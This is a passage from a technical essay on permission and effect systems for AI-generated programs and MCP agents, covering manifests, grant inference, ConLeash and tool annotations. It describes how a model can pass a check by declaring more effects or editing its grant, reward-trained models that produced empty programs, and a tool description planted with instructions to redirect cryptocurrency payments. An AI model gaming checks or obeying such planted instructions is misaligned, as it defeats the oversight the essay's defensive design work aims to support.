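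Sailfin's documentation disagrees about its most important rule. Sailfin's reference page states that a function must declare the effects of every function it calls. The Sailfin guide says that this is planned, and that for now the compiler checks only operations a function uses directly. The difference matters for a program like this:

```
fn send(total: string) ![net] {
    http.post("https://accounts.example/totals", total);
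}
fn report(total: string) {
    send(total);
}
```

The compiler rejects `report` under the rule on the reference page, because `report` calls `send` without declaring `net`. The rule in the guide allows this, and anyone who read only the first line of `report` would think it had no effects. Compiling this code would show which rule the installed version follows. Until then, a cautious user would combine the declarations of every function in the program and its libraries.

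Nexus requires a function to list its permissions, such as `require { PermNet, PermConsole }`. According to Nexus' *Design*, the compiler checks this list and WASI enforces it again at run time. The run-time check limits a generated program only if the host decides which permissions to supply instead of copying the program's own list. Nexus also requires programmers to label every argument, on the theory that models handle explicit information better than information they have to infer. *Design* presents this theory as an observation and gives no measurements.

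*Vercel Labs Builds a Programming Language Designed for AI Agents* reports that the engineer Chris Tate built Zero at Vercel Labs. Coddy's *Agent-First Design*, a tutorial from a company outside the project, explains that a function can reach the outside world only if it receives a value called `World`. `World` is a single category, so it has the same weakness as Haskell's `IO`. Zero's compiler returns errors as structured data with a fixed error code and, when possible, a repair plan that software can apply. Coddy calls the language experimental and advises against using it for customers' software.

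### When the model changes the declaration instead

A model can make an effect error disappear without removing the effect. If the sales program declares {FileRead, Net} and calls `write_file`, the model can delete the call or add `FileWrite` to the declaration. Either change removes the error if the compiler only compares the code with its declaration.

Call the declared set D. Safety requires two comparisons:

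E ⊆ D and D ⊆ G

One comparison checks that a program's declared effects, D, cover everything the code does, and another checks that the grant, G, permits those effects. If the model writes D and nothing performs the second comparison, the model can always pass by declaring more effects. If the model can also edit G, the second comparison gives no protection either.

A model can add a missing effect to a function's signature without being malicious, because that is often the compiler's suggested fix. When a Sailfin function writes a file without declaring `io`, the error message includes a suggestion to add `io` to the signature, and according to the guide, readers can usually copy such suggestions directly. Ronacher has experimented with a tool that adds missing effect markers automatically. This is convenient for testing, which is his purpose, because a marker for the clock shows which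 functions need a fake clock, but as a permission system the tool would approve every program.

AILANG's developers describe a future arrangement in which one agent changes a program and another checks that its effects have not changed. In their example, the first agent makes a function save a copy of its settings to disk. The second agent objects, and the first may remove the change or declare the new effect. But the function already declares `FS`, which in AILANG covers both reading and writing files, so comparing the two declarations would show no difference.

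The grant must therefore be stored where neither the model nor its program can change it. So must anything that can switch off the check, such as compiler options, build files and the list of trusted packages. A coding agent that can write to the whole project folder can usually edit all of these, so they belong outside that folder. Scopes need the same protection, because when TACIT refuses to open a file outside `/reports`, the easiest fix is to request access to a larger folder.

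The wording of the error can also help. The message in the sales example lists the available effects and doesn't suggest adding another. It could also include an instruction to report the task as impossible if those effects aren't enough. Otherwise the model may delete an operation that the task needs. A sales program without its `post` line would fit the grant but never deliver the total, so generated programs also need tests of their results.

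TACIT's retry figures count repeated attempts without separating programs that dropped an operation from programs that requested more access, so they don't show how often models choose the wrong fix. The empty programs in Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues' training runs show that models can learn to satisfy a check without doing the work. But those models were trained with a reward, and a model that only reads error messages may behave differently.

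Anyone who runs such a loop can measure this by keeping every draft and using software to count how often the declared effects or scopes grew from one draft to the next. The trial should include tasks that the grant makes impossible, such as saving the total to a file without `FileWrite`, because the model must then either admit that it can't do the task or try to get around the limit.

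## Setting the grant for each program and revising the list

Every check described so far compares a program with a grant already chosen for it. A manager can choose the grant by hand for the sales program, because it is ten lines long and does a familiar job, but an organisation that runs hundreds of generated programs a day needs a rule for choosing grants. The organisation could use a default for each kind of task, a manifest from the program's author, or a grant worked out from the code or the user's request.

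### A default for each kind of task

An administrator can set a default grant once for each kind of program, such as {FileRead, Net} for monthly reports and {FileRead, FileWrite} for photo conversions. This takes little effort, and the model that writes the program doesn't influence the grant. But the default applies to every program of its kind, so if one monthly report in fifty needs to save a chart, the administrator must either allow all fifty to write files or let that one fail.

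*Permissions on the Loose* (2026) examines serverless applications, which consist of small functions that a cloud provider runs on demand. In 89% of the applications, a single policy applied to every function, and 74% of the permissions in such policies could be removed. Where each function had its own policy, the figure was 41%. Applications that combined a shared policy with separate ones had the highest share of removable permissions, 88%, so narrow grants may help little while a broad default stays in force.

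Sometimes nobody chose the default. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) gives the example of a user who connects an agent to GitHub with an older kind of access key. If the key carries the `repo` permission, the agent can use about 40 tools, including 16 that can write, in every project the user can access.

A default that is too broad shows up in the logs as permissions that hardly any program of that kind uses. One that is too narrow repeatedly causes the same refusal.

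### A manifest from the author

An author usually knows better than an administrator what a program needs. Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2026), in *AgentBound*, designed a manifest for MCP servers, the programs that supply tools to agents through the Model Context Protocol. Many of these servers run with all of their user's permissions. The manifest contains a short description in English and a list of capabilities, which here are names on a fixed list. A server that reported sales totals might have this one, in simplified form:

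```
description:  Adds up a sales file and posts the total
capabilities: mcp.ac.filesystem.read
              mcp.ac.network.client
```

There are 18 capabilities, in five groups:

| Group | Capabilities |
|---|---|
| Files | Read, write, delete |
| System | Read environment variables, set them, run commands, inspect or stop processes |
| Network | Connect to other computers, accept connections, use Bluetooth |
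| Peripherals | Camera, microphone, speaker, screen capture |
| Other | Location, notifications, reading the clipboard, writing to it |

Bühler and colleagues drew up the list by collecting 16 uses of AI agents from 11 papers and matching each to Android's permissions. They dropped permissions that only make sense on a phone, merged near-duplicates such as precise and approximate location, and added environment variables, processes and the clipboard. To look for gaps, they had a model describe 296 popular servers twice, once with this list and once with Android's full list. A few servers that control a connected phone seemed to need phone permissions such as reading text messages, but they control the phone by running commands, which the shorter list already covers.

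The manifest's author chooses the categories of access a server may request. When the server starts, the user sets the scopes within those categories by approving particular folders and addresses. The system stops the server if it requests something outside the manifest's categories.

Program authors have a reason to declare too many permissions, because an unnecessary one never makes their program fail. Manifests also accumulate permissions over time. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, describes servers that gain permissions with each new feature and keep them after the feature is removed. Comparing the manifest with the code can reveal both problems, but not a malicious author who has declared every permission the attack needs. When a model writes the program, the manifest is therefore only a request for permissions.

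### A grant worked out from the code

Bühler and colleagues also built a generator, so that authors could correct a manifest instead of writing one. A small model reads a server's code and documentation and lists the capabilities the server needs, with a reason for each. It does this five times, and a stronger model merges the drafts. Software rejects any capability that isn't on the list. Running the generator on all 296 servers with both lists cost $99.25, or about 17 cents per manifest.

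Bühler and colleagues sent the results to the developers of 96 servers. Of these, 71 never replied, 17 accepted the manifest, 4 rejected it and 4 were still discussing it. The 80.9% accuracy they report is therefore 17 out of the 21 that accepted or rejected the manifest. One developer objected that the server never read local files. Another wanted access to particular environment variables instead of all of them. The system handles this as a scope when the server starts.

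Two of the researchers also wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, which took each of them eight hours. They counted each of 17 capabilities per server as a yes-or-no answer, and the generator agreed with them on 787 of the 816 answers, or 96.5%. Agreement is high partly because most servers lack most of the capabilities. The four most common ones come to about three per server, so even an empty manifest would match roughly four answers in five. The generator got every answer right for only 28 of the 48 servers.

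It is unclear whether the generator more often omitted needed capabilities or listed unneeded ones. Bühler and colleagues write that 23 of the 29 wrong answers were omissions, which would make a working server fail. But they also report that 94% of the capabilities the generator listed were right and that it found 96% of those needed. If omissions were more common, the second figure should be lower than the first.

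Other tools infer permissions without relying on a model's reading of the code. Capslock follows calls through Go programs, and *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) combines a search for risky code patterns with monitoring of the server in a sandbox. With any of these tools, a grant copied from a malicious program's code would include every permission the attack needs.

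*SkillScope* (2026) analyses skills, which are packages of instructions and code that an agent loads for a certain kind of work. It uses a model to judge whether each sensitive action in a skill is necessary for the user's task. If an action is necessary only for some tasks, SkillScope adds a condition to the skill so that the action runs only for those.

### What AgentBound blocked

AgentBound runs each server in a container that enforces the manifest and the user's choices. The container gives the server access only to the approved folders, each either read-only or writable, and passes on only the approved environment variables. A firewall limits the server's connections. A writable folder also allows deletion, so writing and deleting are a single permission in practice, although the list separates them.

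Bühler and colleagues tested it on 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections. By their account of each case, it stopped all the attacks involving eight servers, some of those involving a ninth, and none involving the other five. One of the eight, a map server, secretly swapped its web address for an attacker's, and the firewall blocked the new address.

The failures were attacks that stayed within the grant or never accessed a file, ran a command or opened a connection. One server only reported the time, but its description contained instructions for the model to redirect cryptocurrency payments made through a different server. Another server needed to use a database, and attackers could insert commands into its queries.

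The manifests in these tests were better than an organisation could count on having. For the map server and three others, Bühler and colleagues used manifests generated from the original, harmless versions. They wrote the remaining ten themselves. The results therefore show what the container can enforce when the manifest grants the right permissions.

The protection adds little delay. Servers took roughly 0.1 to 0.4 seconds longer to start, and operations such as reading a file took on average 0.6 milliseconds longer on a Mac and 0.3 on Linux. But the network limit has two weaknesses. The firewall works with numerical addresses, which unrelated websites can share. It also takes effect only after the container has installed the server's package, and some packages run code during installation.

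### A grant worked out from the request

The request "add up last month's sales and report the total to accounts" suggests the grant {FileRead, Net} before anyone writes any code. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) argues that organisations used to grant permissions by job role only because nobody could set up a person's access separately for every task. An agent's task arrives as text, so software can set its access each time. The paper adds, correctly, that an agent can't misuse a credential it never receives, however capable it is. This helps only if the software withholds the right credentials.

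Ordinary requests often omit details that determine which permissions a program needs. "Report the total", for example, could mean sending an e-mail, making a web request or creating a file in a shared folder. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) points out that an agent has no developer to write its policy, only a user who may know nothing about security, and suggests an assistant that asks the user for the missing details. The assistant needs to ask about the task, because "Should accounts receive it by e-mail?" is much easier to answer than "Allow network access?"

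A request can also contain someone else's words. *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (2025) includes a sample prompt that tells a model to choose the permitted tools from the user's query and to allow trusted web domains that the query mentions. If the manager pastes a customer's e-mail into the request, the model could also allow domains that the customer mentioned. The organisation should keep its own list of trusted domains, and the model should receive only the manager's words when it chooses the grant.

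An administrator can easily test for errors of this kind by wording the same task in twenty ways and checking whether the grants differ. If "send accounts the total" produces `Net` and "let accounts know the total" adds `FileWrite`, the model's grants depend on the wording as well as the task.

Working out the grant from the request also makes the check on the code more useful. If E comes from the code and G from the request, a program with a deletion that the request doesn't call for fails E ⊆ G.

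### Permissions that widen one step at a time

Even a good first grant may need to change during a long session. In *Options, Not Clicks*, Li and colleagues describe two ways that one lasting approval of a tool can cover too much. In effect escalation, a user lets a file tool list a folder, and the same approval later lets it delete the folder. In scope escalation, the approval lets the tool do the same thing somewhere else, as with the file-search tool that could search the whole home folder.

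Their system, ConLeash, describes each call by where the data comes from, where it goes, whether it is sensitive, and which effects the call has. The effects are reading, writing, deleting, executing and spawning (starting another process). A new call needs no question if every part of its description fits within the same part of an earlier approval. For files, the order is

one file ⊑ its folder ⊑ the whole computer

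where ⊑ means "fits within". Effects follow the ordinary subset rule.

Suppose the manager has let the agent read ordinary files in `/reports`. This grant covers reading `june.csv` in that folder, but not deleting it, because {delete} isn't a subset of {read}, or reading the payroll, which is in another folder. ConLeash then offers a few choices that each move one step up the order, such as the file, its folder, or the folder above, and choosing a larger folder doesn't add an effect.

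Li and colleagues tested ConLeash on 984 sequences of tool calls that a language model generated and the researchers reviewed. ConLeash allowed 98.3% of the harmless calls and caught 99.4% of those that required asking the user or refusing. The researchers also replayed 50 real sessions from six developers. Of the 1,435 calls in these sessions, 291 went beyond what the user had approved. ConLeash caught 278 of them, Claude Code's auto mode caught 6, and a lasting approval of the whole tool caught none.

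That comparison puts auto mode at a disadvantage, because auto mode is designed to detect dangerous actions, not to track what a user has approved. Li and colleagues also used their own definition of a boundary to judge which calls crossed one. Still, one of the calls that auto mode allowed deleted a folder outside the project the developer was working on, in a different project, and most people would want to know about that.

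Comparing a call with earlier approvals takes 8.2 milliseconds, but a language model first has to describe the call, which takes 4.7 seconds without caching. If it describes two similar calls differently, the user gets an unnecessary question or, worse, doesn't get a necessary one.

Users can also write fixed rules in plain language. In the study of 16 people, ConLeash turned 45 of their 48 rules into working ones, but "don't touch my photos" was too vague. ConLeash stopped 86% of the generated sequences that broke such a rule using one server, and 74% of those using several. Some rules needed a distinction that its categories lack, such as the one between colleagues and outsiders in "never add external attendees to calendar events".

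### Four hints about each tool

MCP has a very short list of its own. A server's author can attach four yes-or-no annotations to each tool:

| Annotation | Question | If the author leaves it out |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Does the tool leave everything as it was? | No |
| `destructiveHint` | If it changes things, could it destroy something? | Yes |
| `idempotentHint` | Is it safe to repeat the same call? | No |
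| `openWorldHint` | Does it deal with people or systems outside? | Yes |

Each annotation defaults to its most dangerous value, so leaving one out can only make a tool look more dangerous. For the sales program, `read_file` would be marked as read-only and as having no contact with outside systems. `post` would be marked as neither, and calling it twice would report the total twice.

These are hints because nobody checks them, so an author can mark a tool read-only even if it deletes files. The Model Context Protocol's Java documentation, *Record Class McpSchema.ToolAnnotations*, therefore tells clients (the programs that connect an agent to servers) never to base decisions about using a tool on hints from an untrusted server. The Model Context Protocol Blog reports that Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked during the original review how a client could use a flag it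 can't trust. The maintainers left each client to decide how much weight to give the hints.

Clients most often use tool annotations to decide when to ask the user for confirmation. According to *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary* (2026), a post on a personal blog, OpenAI's Codex may run read-only tools without asking, but always asks about destructive tools and also asks about tools that change something outside. The post puts the `readOnlyHint` check first, so a read-only tool that fetches web pages may run without confirmation. But fetching a page can leak data if the program puts the data in the URL, so clients need to consider whether a tool is read-only together with whether it reaches outside systems.

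*When Neither Side Confirms* (2026) estimates that about nine in ten destructive tools have no confirmation step on the server, so confirmation usually depends on the client.

Many tool authors fill in the hints without conveying much. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (2026) surveyed 98,291 tools in the official registry in July 2026. `destructiveHint` was present on 65.8%, but mostly on read-only tools, where it has no meaning. It was informative on 12.9%, and only 3.1% of all tools were marked as destructive. One large publisher accounts for much of this pattern. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) describes a different collection of 1,856 tools, of which only 325 had any annotations.

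An organisation with its own effect list can generate the hints from it. StackOne, a company that sells connectors for agents, marks an action read-only if all its effects are reading or searching, and destructive if any of them is deletion. The second rule can miss destructive actions. In StackOne's example, a database query has the effect `execute`, so it wouldn't be marked destructive even though a query can erase a table.

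### Whether to add more hints

Five proposals for new annotations or similar features were open when the maintainers wrote their post. GitHub and OpenAI wrote one of them after finding gaps in their own use of MCP. The best argument for new annotations is that the four existing hints can't describe the combination that leads to data theft, which the programmer Simon Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. No hint covers the first, and `openWorldHint` doesn't distinguish between the other two. MCP Blog (2026), an unofficial site, describes a proposed `sensitiveHint` for private data and an `egressHint` for tools that can send data out. A client could then stop an agent from sending anything after it had read both private data and a stranger's e-mail.

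The maintainers have deliberately kept the list short. They want each new hint to change something a client does, since otherwise it only gives authors more to fill in. They also ask whether the hint would be useful from an untrusted server, and whether it helps a client reason about several tools together. They argue that if a hint is worthless unless it is true, a sandbox or another mechanism should enforce the property it describes. An organisation that runs both the server and the client can already attach private labels in a field called `_meta`, and the maintainers recommend trying new ideas there first.

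Companies also want more annotations, while developers of autonomous agents find confirmations a nuisance and prefer sandboxes. None of the clients the maintainers describe let users filter tools by their hints. GitHub's read-only mode comes closest, and about 17% of its users turn it on.

Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists no change to the hints in the July 2026 specification. In late November, the project's list of accepted and finished proposals still included none for annotations. The charter of the project's group that studies them still left open whether to use a few hints or a richer vocabulary. The next specification is due on March 30, 2027, according to Model Context Protocol Blog's *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (2026).

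The maintainers' first question applies to any effect list. A new category isn't worth adding if it would never change what anyone refuses, asks about or logs. Their objection about trust is weaker outside MCP, because a compiler or a sandbox can enforce a category whatever the author writes.

### Measuring how well the list works

An organisation can review its list every few months from its logs, using four measures:

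- Excess authority per grant is, in practice, the number of permitted operations that never appear in the program's logs.
- The share of programs with the broadest category shows whether that category has become a catch-all.
- Refusals of legitimate programs are the harmless programs that the system stopped, as a share of all harmless programs.
- Approvals per task are the questions a person had to answer, divided by the number of finished tasks.

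No single measure is enough, because granting every permission to every program would reduce the last two to zero, and refusing every permission would greatly improve the first. A change is clearly good only if it improves one measure without making another much worse.

The second is the quickest to calculate and gives a useful warning. *Permissions on the Loose* also compared applications with and without wildcards, which are entries that stand for many permissions. Applications with wildcards could drop 98.7% of their permissions, compared with 61.8% for the rest.

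The third requires someone to read a sample of the refused programs, because a log records refusals but not whether they were right. Without this review, a blocked attack counts as a mistake, and the list gets looser each time it blocks one.

Logs also miss rare operations. If a program has run 30 times without writing a file, the chance that it writes one on any given run could still be as high as 10% (at 95% confidence, if the runs are independent). A program that produces a monthly report might write a file only in January, so its reviewer needs a full year of logs.

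### Splitting, merging and scoping

Each pattern in the logs suggests a different change:

| What the logs show | What to change |
|---|---|
| Many programs hold a category but use only its milder operations | Split the category |
| Two categories nearly always appear together and guard against the same harm | Merge them |
| Programs use most of a category's operations, but on few files or hosts | Add a scope |
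| One kind of task keeps causing the same refusal | Change that task's default and leave the list alone |
| People keep approving the same operation on the same folder or host | Replace the question with a lasting grant limited to that folder or host |

Suppose 120 programs hold `FileWrite`, and a year of logs shows that 110 of them only created new files. Splitting the category into `FileCreate` and `FileReplace` could remove those 110 programs' ability to overwrite or delete files. If all 120 had been overwriting files in a single folder, the split would achieve nothing, and a scope limiting them to that folder would be better.

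The split also leaves 120 old grants for a category that no longer exists. If the administrator converts each to both new categories, every program keeps working but none is safer. If the administrator cancels them, all 120 programs stop. Converting each grant to what its program has used narrows 110 of them, but may break a program that overwrites a file only once every two years. The administrator can reduce that risk with a trial period in which the system allows the operations it would have refused but records them. A trial is reasonable for programs that people already trusted with `FileWrite`, but new programs should get the narrower categories from the first day.

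Merging permissions can give existing programs more access than they were granted. If `FileRead` and `FileWrite` become `Files`, a program that could only read files can now overwrite them. Someone must approve those grants again, or the system must keep enforcing the original ones. Adding scopes has no effect on old grants until someone fills them in. The logs are a good source for a first draft of those scopes.

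A grant can also widen without anyone editing the list. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) points out that almost all MCP clients make new tools available as soon as a server offers them. If an update adds `delete_repository`, the agent can use it at once, without the user's knowledge. Programs with `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` gained new powers in much the same way. To prevent this, the system can store the list's version with each grant and refuse operations added after that version until someone has reviewed them.

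Old grants need an owner and an expiry date too. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (Huang, Dai and colleagues, 2026) found that 46.4% of the 6,137 MCP servers it examined either didn't check authorization or reused an earlier approval without checking who was calling. If a server reuses approvals this way, any other program that reaches it could use an approval given to the sales program.

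The work agents do also changes. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026) cites a count of 177,436 MCP tools in which tools that change something external rose from 27% to 65% of usage between November 2024 and February 2026. Defaults chosen when agents mostly read data could be badly out of date little more than a year later.
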